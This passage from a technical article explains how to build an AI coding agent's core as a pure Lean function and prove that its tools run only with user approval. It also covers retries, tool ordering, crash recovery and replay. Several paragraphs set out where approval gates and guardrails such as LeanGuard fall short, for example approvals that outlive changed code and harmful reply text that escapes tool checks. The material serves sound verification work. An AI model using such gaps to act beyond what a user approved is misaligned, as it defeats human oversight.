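  | .ModelFailed req wait jitter =>    -- both times in milliseconds
      if s.asking = some req then
        if s.tries < 3 then
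          let r := s.nextReq
          ({ s with nextReq := r + 1, asking := some r,
                    tries := s.tries + 1, draft := "" },
           [.StartTimer (.retry r) (max wait (1000 * 2 ^ s.tries) + jitter)])
        else ({ s with asking := none }, [])
      else (s, [])
  | .TimerFired (.retry r) =>
      (s, if s.asking = some r then [.AskAgain r] else [])
```

`wait` is the delay the provider requested, or 0. The core waits at least one second before the first retry, two before the second and four before the third. It doesn't retry a fourth time. `AskAgain` sends the stored conversation unchanged, and a successful reply resets `tries` to 0. Because every attempt has its own number, leftover fragments from a failed attempt can't mix with the new reply. If the user presses Escape during a delay, `asking` becomes `none` and the timer has no effect when it fires.

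The earlier limit of six model calls becomes a limit of 24 attempts, plus four for each refusal by the user. Like the limit on tool runs, it holds only if the shell doesn't retry on its own. If the HTTP library silently retried each request up to twice, the limit of 24 would rise to 72. Hidden retries also keep the screen from showing why the agent is slow.

Retries inside the network code make the core shorter, and some are fairly safe. Zero retries a refused or timed-out connection up to three times there, allowing five seconds for each attempt. The server hasn't received the request at that stage, so a retry can't produce a second reply. Zero never retries after the reply has begun, because that would duplicate text on the screen. However, the rest of the program may receive no updates for fifteen seconds or more while the attempts time out.

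`jitter` is a random number that the shell picks and puts into the event. It spreads out retries when a provider has rejected requests from many agents at once. Alternatively, the first event can contain a random seed from which the core computes all later random numbers, but anyone who learns the seed can predict them.

Clock readings enter the core the same way. The shell can attach the time to every event, and the core can subtract one time from another to find how long a test run took. Firezone uses a Rust type that measures only intervals, so a correction to the computer's clock can't make a timeout expire early. For delays, the example uses a command and an event. The *reducer runtime* in ExRatatui, an Elixir library for terminal programs, does the same with its `send_after` command, which delivers a message to the program later. A program that uses timer commands must handle timers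 that fire after they are no longer needed. Firezone's event loop instead looks up the next deadline, so cancelling a deadline leaves no timer behind.

### The screen and the keyboard

A second pure function, `view : State → Screen`, computes what the screen should contain, and the shell draws the result after a step, so no drawing commands are needed. The shell may skip a frame when it is busy, because the next one contains the whole screen, but skipping a `RunTool` would lose an action. Programmers can also test `view` with plain values, for example by checking that the approval prompt for a call shows the same tool and arguments that the table holds for it.

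ExRatatui runs commands only after it has stored and drawn the new state. A program that follows this order shows "running" before the tool starts, so the user can see what is about to happen.

In the example, the shell turns the user's "y" into the event `Approved 2`, taking the id from the prompt on the screen when the key arrives. If `step` instead interpreted the key using the current state, it could approve a call that the user has never read. This would happen if the screen showed the prompt for call 2 and another event replaced it with the prompt for call 3 just before the "y" reached the core. Including the id prevents this mismatch between the screen and the state, but it doesn't help a user who presses "y" a tenth of a second after the prompt changes. It is therefore safer for the core to also ignore approvals that arrive too soon after a prompt appears.

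When the user sends a message during a streamed reply, BoundaryML's agent adds it to a list in the state. The screen shows the message as queued, but the model doesn't receive it until the reply has ended.

*Elm pattern*, the documentation of a terminal program that manages virtual machines, describes a complete interface of this kind. It has about 80 event types and 30 effect types, and it redraws the screen after every step. However, the approval check is in the dispatcher, the code that carries out effects. The core can return "delete this machine" before anyone has approved the deletion, and the dispatcher holds the command back. The core alone therefore doesn't guarantee that every deletion follows an approval, and a proof of that guarantee would have to include the dispatcher.

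### One queue and several tools

Every event in the example passes through one queue, so calls to `step` never overlap and the state has one history. The tools still run in parallel. *L3M* (Eisenach, George and colleagues, 2026), an agent runtime written in Lean, uses the same arrangement, with one "sequencer" that orders all incoming signals and never waits on the outside world. *LogAct* (2026) replaces the loop with several small state machines that read and write one shared log, each waiting for certain kinds of entry. The shared log still gives all the entries a common order.

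The most visible drawback is delay. If a test run prints 20,000 lines, each line is a separate event, and each event takes a millisecond to process and redraw, an Escape press queued behind them waits 20 seconds. The shell can shorten the wait by joining lines that arrive close together, or by keeping key presses in a separate queue that it empties first. It can also limit the queue's length, so that a process that prints too fast has to pause until there is room. `step` must also be fast, because other events wait while it runs, so any long computation belongs in a command.

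When several tools run at once, the order of their results can vary from run to run. Metis removes this variation by returning results to the model in the order of the calls. The core then has to hold early results until the slowest call is done.

The queue also doesn't order the tools' effects on disk. If the model asks for a read and an edit of the same file in one reply, the outcome depends on which tool reaches it first, so the core needs a rule for which calls may overlap. Metis divides foreground calls into those that can run together, those that take turns with one another, and those that must run alone. Yu compared this with running everything in sequence, using two local file operations, a git query and two requests to a test server. Over 30 pairs of runs, the median time fell from 26.0 to 14.1 milliseconds.

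*Small agents should know what their tools do* (2026) derives the order of tool calls from declarations of what each tool reads and writes. Conflicting calls go into successive levels, and calls within a level run in parallel, so each level takes as long as its slowest call. Suppose a reply contains a two-second read of `cart.py`, a three-second read of another file, and a one-second edit of `cart.py`. They take six seconds in sequence and four in levels. A core that checks for newly unblocked calls after every `Exited` event could start the edit after two seconds and finish everything in three. All these schemes rely on correct declarations, since a tool that is labelled read-only but writes can still conflict with another.

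### How git-iris came to bypass its reducer

git-iris has a terminal interface, Iris Studio, whose core is a function called `reduce`. Iris Studio's *Event System* states the rule that all state changes are events, and lists 48 kinds. It also gives an example of a mistake to avoid, in which code writes an agent's result straight into the state. Yet Iris Studio's *Reducer Pattern* concedes that the program is "no longer a fully pure reducer architecture end-to-end".

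Code outside `reduce` now changes the state in two ways. Key handlers update parts of the interface directly, which the documentation says is for "immediate interactions". The main application also applies some results of background work itself. When the git status arrives, for example, a function in the application copies it into the state and then decides whether to generate a commit message automatically, a decision that tests of `reduce` can't cover. According to Iris Studio's *Studio Internals*, the full route from key press to event, reducer, effect and executor adds indirection, which the developers consider worthwhile for work that crosses several screens but not for every local update.

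They change the state in place instead of returning a new one for a separate reason, which is that copying a large state is slow. This does no harm by itself, because Rust's ownership rules stop ordinary code elsewhere from changing the state while `reduce` runs. The result is the same as with a fresh copy.

The reducer in git-iris 2.1.0 also performs I/O, although the comment at the top of the source code says that `reduce` avoids direct I/O. When a file watcher reports a change in the repository, `reduce` reads the current branch from the repository. If the branch has changed, `reduce` saves a session file, loads and saves notes about the branch, and reads the clock. A test of this code needs a real repository, and replaying the same events later can give a different state. The documentation doesn't explain why the reducer performs this I/O.

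The slip was easy to make because the state contains a live connection to the repository and another to the file-watching service. Any code in `reduce` can call them, and Rust allows it. If the state held only plain data, `reduce` would have nothing to call, and the shell would have to read the branch name and put it into the event. git-iris already defines an event with a field for the name, `CompanionBranchSwitch`.

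## What can be proved about the core, and how does the proof go?

The worked example guarantees that the agent starts at most five tools and never runs an edit or the tests unless the user has approved that exact call. Because `step` is a pure function, a programmer can state both guarantees as theorems and prove them for every sequence of events, and so for every possible model. The proofs below use the basic version of `step`, which has five kinds of event and four kinds of command.

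### Runs and invariants

To state a theorem about every run, we first need to define a run. The definition below includes a trace, which lists in order each event passed to `step` and each command `step` returned.

```lean
inductive Entry
  | ev  (e : Event)      -- an event that reached step
  | cmd (c : Command)    -- a command that step returned

inductive Reach : List Entry → State → Prop
  | start : Reach [] s0
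  | next (h : Reach tr s) (e : Event) :
      Reach (tr ++ .ev e :: (step s e).2.map .cmd) (step s e).1
```

`Reach tr s` means that the trace `tr` leads from the starting state `s0` (an empty table, next id 1, fuel 5) to the state `s`. The trace exists only in the proof, so the program doesn't have to store it. The rule `next` puts no condition on the event `e`, so the definition also covers a second "yes", an approval for a call that doesn't exist, and any reply a model could produce.

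An invariant is a statement that is true at the start and that every step keeps true. To prove one, a programmer checks the starting state, then assumes that the statement holds for some trace and state, and shows that it still holds after one more event. By induction, it holds after any number of events. (Many authors call this an "inductive invariant" and use "invariant" for anything true in every reachable state.)

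### At most five tool runs

The trace never contains more than five `RunTool` commands, but induction on that statement alone fails. Suppose a trace contains five `RunTool` commands and the state still has fuel 3. The statement holds, but the next read would add a sixth command. No real run reaches that state, because each tool run uses fuel. The induction works once the statement also relates the number of `RunTool` commands to the remaining fuel.

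```lean
def issued (tr : List Entry) : Nat :=
  tr.countP fun | .cmd (.RunTool _ _) => true | _ => false

theorem fuel_exact   (h : Reach tr s) : issued tr + s.fuel = 5
theorem at_most_five (h : Reach tr s) : issued tr ≤ 5
```

At the start the sum is 0 + 5. The table lists what each event can do to it.

| Event | `RunTool` commands returned | Fuel |
|---|---|---|
| `ModelReplied`, closing message | 0 | unchanged |
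| `ModelReplied`, a read, with fuel left | 1 | falls by 1 |
| `ModelReplied`, a read, with no fuel | 0 | stays at 0 |
| `ModelReplied`, an edit or test run | 0 | unchanged |
| `Approved`, call waiting, with fuel left | 1 | falls by 1 |
| `Approved`, any other case | 0 | unchanged |
| `Denied` or `ToolFinished` | 0 | unchanged |
| `Interrupted` | 0 | unchanged |

The sum stays the same in every row. Fuel is a `Nat` and can't fall below 0, so `at_most_five` follows. In the last row, an interrupt can return a list of any length, so that case also needs a short lemma showing that the list contains only `Kill` commands.

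Lean accepts the proof only if it covers every case. If a programmer later adds a branch that returns `RunTool` without subtracting fuel, the proof stops compiling.

### No edit or test run without approval

The second promise concerns the order of events. *Automating Formal Proofs for Reactive Systems* (Ricketts, Robert and colleagues, 2014) calls this pattern "A Enables B", meaning that every B has an A somewhere before it. In the paper's example, an SSH server (a program for remote logins) may request a terminal for a user only after that same user has authenticated. In the agent, each approval must likewise apply only to its own call, so an approval of call 2 must not start call 3.

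```lean
def Tool.needsApproval : Tool → Prop
  | .read _ => False
  | _       => True

theorem run_ok (h : Reach tr s) (hc : .RunTool id t ∈ (step s e).2) :
    (∀ t', .cmd (.RunTool id t') ∉ tr) ∧
    (t.needsApproval →
       e = .Approved id ∧
       .cmd (.AskUser id t) ∈ tr ∧
       ∀ t', .cmd (.AskUser id t') ∈ tr → t' = t)
```

Suppose a run has reached state `s`, and the event `e` makes `step` return `RunTool id t`. According to the theorem, the trace contains no earlier `RunTool` with that id. If `t` is an edit or a test run, then `e` is the approval of that id, and the core has already asked the user about `t`, and only `t`, under that id.

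A first attempt at an invariant might be "so far, every edit and test run had an approval, and no call ran twice". This is true in every reachable state, but the induction fails again. Nothing in the statement connects the trace to the table of calls, so it allows positions like these two:

- The table lists call 3 as waiting, although the trace already contains `RunTool 3`. The next `Approved 3` starts it a second time.
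- Call 2 is an edit on the user's screen, but the next unused id is still 2. The model proposes a test run, which overwrites the edit in the table. When the user presses "y" for the edit, the tests run.

Such a position is usually called a "counterexample to induction". *Plain and Simple Inductive Invariant Inference for Distributed Protocols in TLA+* (2022) describes the remedy, which is to add statements until every step preserves the whole set. Four statements are enough here.

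```lean
structure Inv (tr : List Entry) (s : State) : Prop where
  fresh : ∀ id, s.calls id ≠ none → id < s.nextId
  shown : ∀ id t, .cmd (.AskUser id t) ∈ tr →
            ∃ st, s.calls id = some (t, st)
  asked : ∀ id t, s.calls id = some (t, .waiting) →
            .cmd (.AskUser id t) ∈ tr
  ran   : ∀ id t, .cmd (.RunTool id t) ∈ tr →
            ∃ st, s.calls id = some (t, st) ∧ st ≠ .waiting
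```

`fresh` means that every id in the table is smaller than the next id. `shown` means that a call's content never changes after the user has seen it. `asked` means that the core has shown the user every waiting call, and `ran` means that a call that has run is never waiting. The statements depend on each other. Without `fresh`, for example, a new proposal could overwrite a finished call with a waiting one, and `ran` would fail.

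At the start the table and the trace are empty, so all four hold. The induction then goes through the events:

- When the model proposes a call, `step` writes only to the row for the next id. By `fresh` that row was empty, so older calls stay as they were. The next id then rises by one, which keeps `fresh` true. If the call needs approval, the same step returns `AskUser` with the same content, so `shown` and `asked` hold for the new row. A read starts as running or finished, never as waiting, so `ran` holds.
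- When the user approves a waiting call, `launch` keeps its content and changes its status to running or finished.
- A refusal or a tool result also keeps the content and sets the status to finished. An interrupt does this to every call.
- Any other event leaves the table alone and returns no commands.

`run_ok` follows from the four statements. If the new command is a read, its id is the next id. By `ran`, an earlier `RunTool` with that id would have a row in the table, but by `fresh` no such row exists. If the command follows an approval, the call was waiting, so by `ran` it has not run before. By `asked`, the user was asked about the call earlier, and by `shown`, no question under the same id had different content. The extended version with timers and exit codes has more cases, but the same four statements still hold.

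*Temporary Authority, Permanent Effects* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) examined seventeen fixed security advisories from three agent products. In twelve of them, the agent did something the approval did not cover, which `run_ok` rules out in the core. In the other five, an approval stayed valid after something it depended on had changed, such as the text of an approved script. `run_ok` allows this because it constrains the content of the call but not the files the call uses. For example, if a user approves a test run and the code changes before the tests start, the changed code runs under the same approval.

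*LEANGUARD* (Sankar, Ganguly and colleagues, 2026) deals with both cases. Its program checks each tool call against a policy written in Lean. A user's confirmation can be used only once, for one exact call, and only while the relevant backend data is unchanged. LeanGuard also records a call before the tool starts, so a single-use action can't run again while its outcome is unknown. The status "running" has the same purpose in the worked example.

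### From the core to the world

The theorems so far are about lists of commands. Proving anything about actual tool runs also requires the faithful-shell assumption, which is that the shell performs the commands issued and no others, no more often than asked, and reports outcomes truthfully. In the code below, `w` lists what has really happened up to some moment, and `tr` is the trace up to the same moment.

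```lean
inductive Fact
  | agreed  (id : Nat) (t : Tool)    -- the user agreed to this call
  | started (id : Nat) (t : Tool)    -- the shell started this tool

structure Faithful (tr : List Entry) (w : List Fact) : Prop where
  noExtras : ∀ id t,
    w.count (.started id t) ≤ tr.count (.cmd (.RunTool id t))
  truthful : ∀ id t, .ev (.Approved id) ∈ tr →
    .cmd (.AskUser id t) ∈ tr → .agreed id t ∈ w

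theorem world_ok (h : Reach tr s) (f : Faithful tr w) :
    starts w ≤ 5 ∧
    ∀ id t, .started id t ∈ w →
      w.count (.started id t) = 1 ∧
      (t.needsApproval → .agreed id t ∈ w)
```

`starts w` is the total number of tools started. It is at most the number of `RunTool` commands in the trace, by `noExtras`, and that number is at most five, by `at_most_five`.

The proof for approval uses the premise twice. Suppose the tests really started as call 3. By `noExtras`, the trace contains `RunTool 3` for a test run. By `run_ok`, it also contains an `AskUser` and an `Approved` for the same call. By `truthful`, the user really agreed. If the premise holds at every moment, it holds just after the tests start, so the user agreed before they started.

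The theorem holds even when the shell fails in some ways. `noExtras` lets the shell do less than the core asked, so a crash before a tool starts breaks neither promise. A false tool result doesn't break them either, because `ToolFinished` never leads directly to a `RunTool`. But `Reach` requires the shell to always pass the latest state to `step`, so the theorem doesn't apply to a shell that reuses an old state.

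Other projects rely on similar assumptions. A property proved in Verdi, a University of Washington framework for verified distributed systems, holds on every execution if Verdi's network model covers everything a real network can do. The theorem of Sankar and colleagues assumes that observations are truthful and that the guard checks every consequential call. *Provably Secure Agent Guardrail* (2026) proves safety by induction on the length of a run, and assumes that actions have no side effects outside the model. In the worked example, an edit tool that also ran a code formatter would break that assumption.

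Ricketts and colleagues show how to weaken the premise. Their system, Reflex, has its own language for event handlers, and they proved once, in the proof assistant Coq (now Rocq), that its interpreter produces only the traces that the mathematical description allows. They still assume that basic operations, such as sending a string over a channel, behave correctly.

### Why finishing is harder to prove

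Both promises are safety properties. If a run breaks one, it does so at an identifiable moment, and nothing later can repair it. *Defining Liveness* (Alpern and Schneider, 1985) defines the other basic kind, a liveness property, which requires something good to happen eventually. No finite beginning of a run can violate a liveness property, because the good thing may still happen. The paper also proves that every property of single runs combines a safety property and a liveness property.

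A core that ignored every event and returned no commands would satisfy all the theorems above. To rule it out, a programmer might prove that the agent finishes its task. Invariants aren't enough for this, so the usual method is to find a quantity that falls with each step and can't fall forever.

It is possible to prove that the agent stops, under some assumptions. Let the stage be 3 while a tool runs, 2 while the agent waits for the model, 1 while it waits for the user, and 0 when it is idle. If nobody interrupts, the following quantity falls with every answer the agent receives:

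```
3 × (fuel + refusals still to come) + stage
```

If the user never refuses, it starts at 3 × 5 + 2 = 17, so the agent stops after at most 17 answers. A user who refused every proposal would keep the agent going forever. The core also can't make answers arrive. A test suite may hang, the provider may never reply, or the user may leave. The timer in the extended version replaces the assumption that the tests finish with the assumption that the operating system eventually ends a killed process.

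yamafaktory's *Formal*, a property checker based on Lean, has a small example of the same problem. Its machine has a counter and two actions, increase and reset. The claim that the counter always returns to zero is false, because a run can choose "increase" forever. With the added assumption that resets keep happening, the claim is true, and the checker accepts a proof supplied with the example.

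Proving that the agent stops also doesn't prove that it fixes the bug. The model can send its closing message at once, and the agent then stops with `cart.py` unchanged. A proof that the bug gets fixed would have to assume that the model eventually proposes a correct edit. Stricter checks don't help guarantee a fix, and can even prevent one. In *Proof-Carrying Contracts* (2026), a call runs only if the agent supplies a proof with it, which preserves the safety guarantee but may cause the task to fail.

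### Why secrecy needs several runs

Suppose the project contains a password, and the user wants nothing the agent sends to the model provider to depend on it. Searching one trace for the password isn't enough, because the agent might send it in an encoded form, or reveal one letter of it by whether it reads a second file. To find out whether the output depends on the password, a programmer has to compare two runs in which only the password differs.

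Clarkson and Schneider (2009), in *Hyperproperties*, call properties of whole sets of runs hyperproperties. Finkbeiner (2025), in *Logics and Algorithms for Hyperproperties*, surveys the logics and algorithms developed for them since. A common proof method is self-composition, which involves treating two copies of a system as one system and finding an invariant of the pair. Schneider, in *Verifying Hyperproperties with Temporal Logic of Actions (TLA)*, uses this method so that existing tools for single runs can also check secrecy.

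In the worked example, the method shows that tool output can't directly influence the core's decisions. If two runs have the same events except for the text the tools return, their states stay equal after every event because `step` never examines that text, and their commands differ only in the text of `AskModel`. The example doesn't keep the password secret, however, because the model provider receives the tool output in full. *PerMIT* (2026) proves a theorem about pairs of agent runs in Lean, and a later section discusses secrecy for agents.

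### Why an approved edit can still be bad

`run_ok` does not depend on what an edit does to the program. Suppose the model proposes replacing the body of `total` with `return 5`. The only test, `total([2, 3])`, passes. If the user approves the edit, every theorem still holds, but the shop now charges 5 for every purchase. To exclude this edit, someone would have to specify what `total` should compute and prove that the new code computes it. That would be a separate theorem, about the shop's code rather than the agent's.

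The same gap appears between a written policy and its formal version. Sankar and colleagues tested LeanGuard on customer-service tasks, where it blocked every call that the Lean policy forbade. A judge model still found a breach of the original written policy in 6.5% of episodes with the guard and feedback, compared with 9.7% without a guard. Their audit found mistakes by the judge, but also requirements missing from the Lean policy and incorrect records of user consent. The guard also checks only tool calls, so attacks that put the harm in the reply's text still succeeded in 30.2% of guarded customer-service and travel episodes.

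### Cheaper checks

Several weaker checks take less effort than a full proof and find many of the same mistakes. One is exhaustive search. To keep the search small, we can limit the model to sending a closing message or proposing one fixed read, one fixed edit or a test run. If ids also stop at 3 and tool output is empty, the example has 14 possible events. There are then 2,744 sequences of three events, including the double approval. There are about 289 billion sequences of ten, but many lead to the same state. yamafaktory's checker visits each state only once and returns a shortest sequence that breaks the rule.

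*Towards Verifiably Safe Tool Use for LLM Agents* (2026) uses the analyser Alloy to run this kind of search on a model of an agent's tools. Alloy quickly finds a way for private data to reach an outside email when there are no restrictions, but finds none once restrictions are added, while harmless tasks such as rescheduling an event remain possible.

Search can also test an invariant before anyone tries to prove it. In *Formal Verification of a Distributed Dynamic Reconfiguration Protocol* (2021), the TLC model checker searched for steps from a state that satisfied the proposed invariant to one that didn't. This works only on small instances and is not a proof, but the later proof revealed no errors in the invariant. Finding the invariant still took much human insight. yamafaktory's checker now searches for the missing statements itself, and because Lean checks the result, a wrong guess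 only wastes time.

Property-based tests take even less work. The programmer states a rule, such as "no call runs twice", and a library tries it on thousands of random inputs. If the library draws approval ids from all 64-bit numbers, though, almost every approval is for a call that doesn't exist, so nearly all the tests exercise only the branch that ignores it. In an article on Rust code written by AI agents, johncylee warns of this problem and recommends random tests for the shell and formal checks for the pure core, where the extra computation is worthwhile.

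Kani checks a Rust function for all inputs up to a chosen size. In Pi's *agent-formal-verify*, a package of instructions for coding agents, Kani is for production functions with bounded inputs and loops, and TLA+, a language for modelling systems, is for problems with threads. The package also has the agent introduce mistakes to make sure that each check can fail.

A programmer can use Kani to check that `step` preserves an invariant. The proof harness takes any table of up to four calls and any event, assumes that the invariant holds, runs `step` once, and checks that the invariant still holds. This limits the size of the table but not the length of the run.

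Suppose a Rust version of the core stores the next id in one byte. In an ordinary optimised build, the counter returns to 0 after 255, and new calls soon overwrite old ones. A user can cause this without using any fuel by repeatedly refusing proposals.

| Check | What it covers | Does it find the one-byte id? |
|---|---|---|
| Random tests of the Rust code | the sequences drawn | only with more than 255 proposals in a sequence |
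| Search to depth ten | every sequence of ten events from chosen values | no |
| Kani, one step from any small table | every id and every event | yes, at id 255 |
| Lean proof about the Lean `step` | every run of the Lean function | no, because a `Nat` has no upper limit |

### Proofs about the running code and proofs about a model

The proof in the last row of the table is correct, but it is about a different program from the one the agent runs. The problem disappears if the agent runs the Lean function itself. Eisenach and colleagues work this way in L3M, where the theorems are about checks in the code that runs. *Agenra* (2026) has some proofs about deployed functions and others about companion models. yamafaktory's checker compares a Lean model with the source code on sample inputs, but its documentation states clearly that this doesn't prove the model is faithful. johncylee calls it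 "translation drift" when an AI agent proves a design in one language and then writes something different in another.

Refinement connects the two with a proof that the simple model could also do everything the fast program does. *Stateful Services*, a tutorial for the proof language F*, demonstrates this on a network calculator that stores up to ten integers. The model is a short pure function called `step`, which takes a stack and a request and returns a stack and a response. The program that runs is about 300 lines of C, generated from verified low-level code.

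The proof relates the bytes received and the bytes sent to a state of the simple model. For each message the program accepts, the proof must show that the received bytes form a valid request, that `step` gives the new state, and that the sent bytes encode the response from `step`. A further condition prevents the program from replacing its earlier history. Without it, the program could satisfy the proof after each message by using a different history that never happened.

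An AI agent wrote the implementation and proof, which take about 4,500 lines. A reviewer has to read only the simple model and confirm that the proof refers to it. An agent's developers could use the same method to prove `run_ok` for a short core and run a faster one. They would still have to trust the translation to C, the C compiler and the operating system.

Refinement preserves both promises of the worked example, because removing runs from a safe set leaves a safe set. It may not preserve secrecy. Clarkson and Schneider give the example of a system that may output 0, 1 or a secret bit, so its possible outputs are 0 and 1 whatever the secret is. A version that always outputs the secret bit does only what the original could do, but it reveals the secret.

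*Lean4Agent* (Wang, Huang and colleagues, 2026) proves properties only of a model of an agent's workflow. The model, written in Lean, is a graph of steps, each with conditions that must hold before it and conditions that should hold after it. Lean checks that earlier steps establish what later steps need. In one faulty workflow, a step had to verify a fix using evidence from a previous step, but the conversation it received didn't include that evidence.

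The check is useful in practice. Wang and colleagues tested three workflows that passed the check and three that failed it, using five models and 50 hard programming problems. The passing workflows solved 58.3% of the problems on average, and the failing ones solved 43.5%. With only six workflows, some of the difference may come from other ways the passing workflows were better.

Wang and colleagues' proof assumes that whenever a step's starting conditions hold, the model can produce a result that meets the step's final conditions. This is a much stronger assumption than `run_ok` needs, since `run_ok` assumes nothing about the model, but `run_ok` also guarantees nothing about the quality of the work. Because their proof depends on this assumption, they also check the results of actual runs. In one run on a bug in the Django web framework, the workflow had passed the Lean check, but its verification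 step accepted a fix while tests were still failing.

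## What survives a crash, a replay or a fork?

Because `step` is a pure function, a list of past events is enough to recover an agent's state. The shell appends every event to a log file and, after a restart, applies `step` to the logged events in order.

```lean
def rebuild (log : List Event) : State :=
  log.foldl (fun s e => (step s e).1) s0
```

`foldl` starts from `s0` and takes in one event at a time. The `.1` keeps the new state and discards the commands, so rebuilding the state doesn't run any tools or call the model. If the log contains the first seven events of the bug fix, up to `Approved 3`, the rebuilt state has call 3 running, next id 4 and fuel 2, as it did before the restart.

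The shell must save each event before it carries out the resulting commands. Otherwise it could start the tests and crash before saving `Approved 3`. The rebuilt state would then show call 3 as waiting, and a second "yes" from the user would run the tests again. L3M, the Lean runtime by Eisenach and colleagues, also stores its records before it starts any activity. The shell must also save the full text of each model reply to restore the conversation, because `ModelReplied` contains only the tool call.

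Folding the log reproduces the old state only if `step` and `s0` haven't changed. Suppose a new release lowers the starting fuel from 5 to 2, and a user loads the old log. The read and the edit use up both units, so at `Approved 3` the new version closes call 3 without returning a `RunTool`, although the tests did run. It then ignores the result "1 passed". Saving the starting state in the log prevents this particular error. The Decider pattern described earlier also handles rule changes, because its log records decisions, such as "started the tests", so a new version doesn't make them again.

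### A crash during the test run

Suppose the harness dies just after the shell receives `RunTool 3`. The log ends with `Approved 3`, and any of these may have happened:

- The tests never started.
- They started and died with the harness.
- They are still running, as a process without a parent.
- They finished, but the harness died before it saved the result.

The log is the same in all four cases, so `rebuild` returns the same state, and no rule in the core can distinguish the cases.

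Other commands are easier to recover. The basic agent does one thing at a time, so only the commands from the last event can be unfinished.

| Last event in the log | Unfinished command | After the restart |
|---|---|---|
| `ToolFinished 2` | `AskModel` | Ask again. The provider may charge twice and the reply may differ, but the agent never acted on the lost reply. |
| `ModelReplied` (run the tests) | `AskUser 3` | Show the question again. |
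| `Approved 3` | `RunTool 3` | The tests may or may not have run. |

To keep the recovery policy in the core, the shell can add an event, `Restarted`, after it has rebuilt the state.

```lean
  | .Restarted =>
      let id := s.nextId - 1          -- the latest call
      match s.calls id with
      | some (t, .running) =>
          (s.put id t .finished,
           [.AskModel "Restarted. The last call may or may not have run."])
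      | some (t, .waiting) => (s, [.AskUser id t])
      | _                  => (s, [])
```

This branch never returns a `RunTool`, so both theorems about the core still hold. If the model wants to run the tests again, it has to propose call 4, which needs a new approval and another unit of fuel. (To resend a lost model request, the core also needs the `asking` field from the extended version.)

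### Recording before or after the action

More records don't remove the uncertainty. AWS's *Idempotency and retries*, a guide to writing programs that survive crashes, offers two settings for a step with effects. By default, the program acts without waiting for a "start" record to be stored, and repeats the step after a crash. In the other setting, the program waits until the record is safely stored before it acts. After a crash, it marks the step as interrupted instead of repeating it automatically. The table shows how often the action happens under each setting.

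| Policy after a restart | Crash just before the action | Crash just after the action |
|---|---|---|
| Repeat the step | once | twice |
| Don't repeat it | never | once |

Saving a record and running the tests are separate operations, and the harness can always crash between them. After the restart, the program can find the same log whether or not the tests ran, so it has to guess whether to run them again or skip them, and each choice is wrong in one case. AWS also warns that the "don't repeat" setting applies to a single attempt, so a separate retry rule can still run the step again.

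The exception is an effect that commits in the same transaction as its record, which can work when both are writes to the same database. Sending an email or running tests can't be part of such a transaction.

Temporal is a durable-execution engine, which means it records a program's progress so the program can resume after a crash. It calls a step with effects an "activity". Temporal's *Activity Definition* describes a worker that completes an activity but crashes just before reporting the completion. Temporal then runs the activity again, which could charge the customer twice in a payment system. Temporal guarantees only that an activity with retries will be "observed as completed exactly once", however many times it ran.

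### Keys and checks

An operation is idempotent if performing it twice has the same result as performing it once. The edit to `cart.py` is idempotent, but an edit that replaces `import os` with the two lines `import os` and `import sys` is not, because repeating it adds a second `import sys`.

The usual remedy for payments and posts is an idempotency key, a unique key that the client sends with the request. The service ignores any further request with the same key. This works only if a retry uses the original key. AWS tells programmers to generate the key inside a recorded step, because a key generated elsewhere changes on replay. Temporal suggests combining the run's id with the activity's id. In the worked example, a run number and the call id would do, since the fold reproduces the call id. *Verified Tool Calls Improve LLM Agent Reliability Under Non-Atomic Failures* (Mansoor, Phadke and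 Rana, 2026) computes the key from the agent, the action, its content and a block of time. A retry that falls into the next block would get a new key.

Letting the model make the retry causes a similar problem. According to *Always-On Agents* (2026), a survey of agents with persistent state, an agent restored from a checkpoint writes slightly different requests, which outside services treat as new. The `Restarted` branch above has this weakness, because the model's new proposal becomes call 4 and gets a new key. For a payment tool, reissuing `RunTool 3` under its old id would be better. But `run_ok` forbids a second `RunTool` with the same id, so the programmer would have to weaken the theorem to allow repeats after a restart and add the service's key handling to the trusted base.

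If the service doesn't accept keys, the agent can check whether the action happened before repeating it. *Where Does Exactly-Once Live?* (Li, 2026) proves that checking isn't enough if the first request may still be in transit. Until a delayed request takes effect, every check returns the same answer as if the request had been lost. The agent has to resend a lost request to finish the task, so it also resends a delayed one that takes effect after it stops waiting, and the action happens twice. If the agent knows the longest possible delay, it can wait that long and then check. The orphaned test run above is a local version of the same problem.

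Li also measured how often this happens, in 25,930 runs with nine models and simulated services for billing, email and similar tasks. The six strongest models had instructions to do everything exactly once. When an action had succeeded and only the reply was lost, they duplicated it in 0.5% of runs, because they checked first. The rate was 56% when the request was still in transit and 74% when the network delivered the request twice.

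In a comparison with four models, accepting keys on every write cut duplicates from 28% to 4%. No duplicates occurred when an agent retried a delayed request with its original key. Most of the remaining duplicates came from agents that had sent no key the first time. A core that attaches the call id as a key would prevent that mistake.

When the delay was always 90 seconds, 99% of runs with a two-minute wait performed each action exactly once. When delays ranged from 40 seconds to two hours, 84% of runs with a wait of up to an hour did so, and the average run took 50 minutes of simulated time. With keys attached automatically, 94% of runs performed each action exactly once, and a run took a minute and a half.

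Silent retries below the model cut the share of exactly-once runs from 72% to 50%. In 90% of the runs with a duplicate, the agent reported the task as completed, so users can't rely on its final message to find the error. When a service offered no way to check whether a write had succeeded, the strongest models usually asked a human operator and duplicated 13% of the affected writes, compared with 28% to 31% when they could check. Asking the user is therefore a reasonable recovery for a tool without idempotency keys, provided the user can find out what happened.

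### Seven meanings of "replay"

*The Log is the Agent* (Nakajima, May 2026) presents ActiveGraph, an agent system in which many small "behaviours" react to changes in a shared graph. The graph is a fold over the log. Behaviours may call models and tools, and ActiveGraph records the replies so that a replay can reuse them. Nakajima claims that this design provides deterministic replay, low-overhead forks and a traceable origin for every result.

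Three months later, Nakajima audited those claims in the replay study cited earlier. He was checking his own system, though he reports several results that count against it. The study distinguishes seven things people mean when they say a run can be replayed. The last column shows how each applies to the bug fix.

| Meaning | What has to match | How it could fail in the bug fix |
|---|---|---|
| Byte | the saved file | a program saves the same log with different spacing |
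| Trace | the events and their order | a copy of the log lacks an event |
| Projection | the state computed from the events | a new release changes the starting fuel |
| Path | the sequence of model calls and tools | a new run tests before it edits |
| Decision | the conclusion of the task | a new run decides that the code is correct |
| Execution | the code runs again on recorded results, with no live calls | the result of call 3 is missing |
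| Environment | the outside world and the log | someone has changed `cart.py` since |

None of these implies all the others. For example, a new run can reach the same decision by another path, and a perfect copy of a log may lack the results needed to run the code again.

Nakajima then examined 5,540 public logs from an archived experiment called Synthetic Players, which ran on ActiveGraph. A log with n events can be cut in n + 1 places, so the logs have 317,296 possible cuts in total. For each cut, Nakajima assessed what a new run could safely do with the events before it.

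| Question | Yes | With conditions | No |
|---|---|---|---|
| Can the state be rebuilt? | 317,296 | 0 | 0 |
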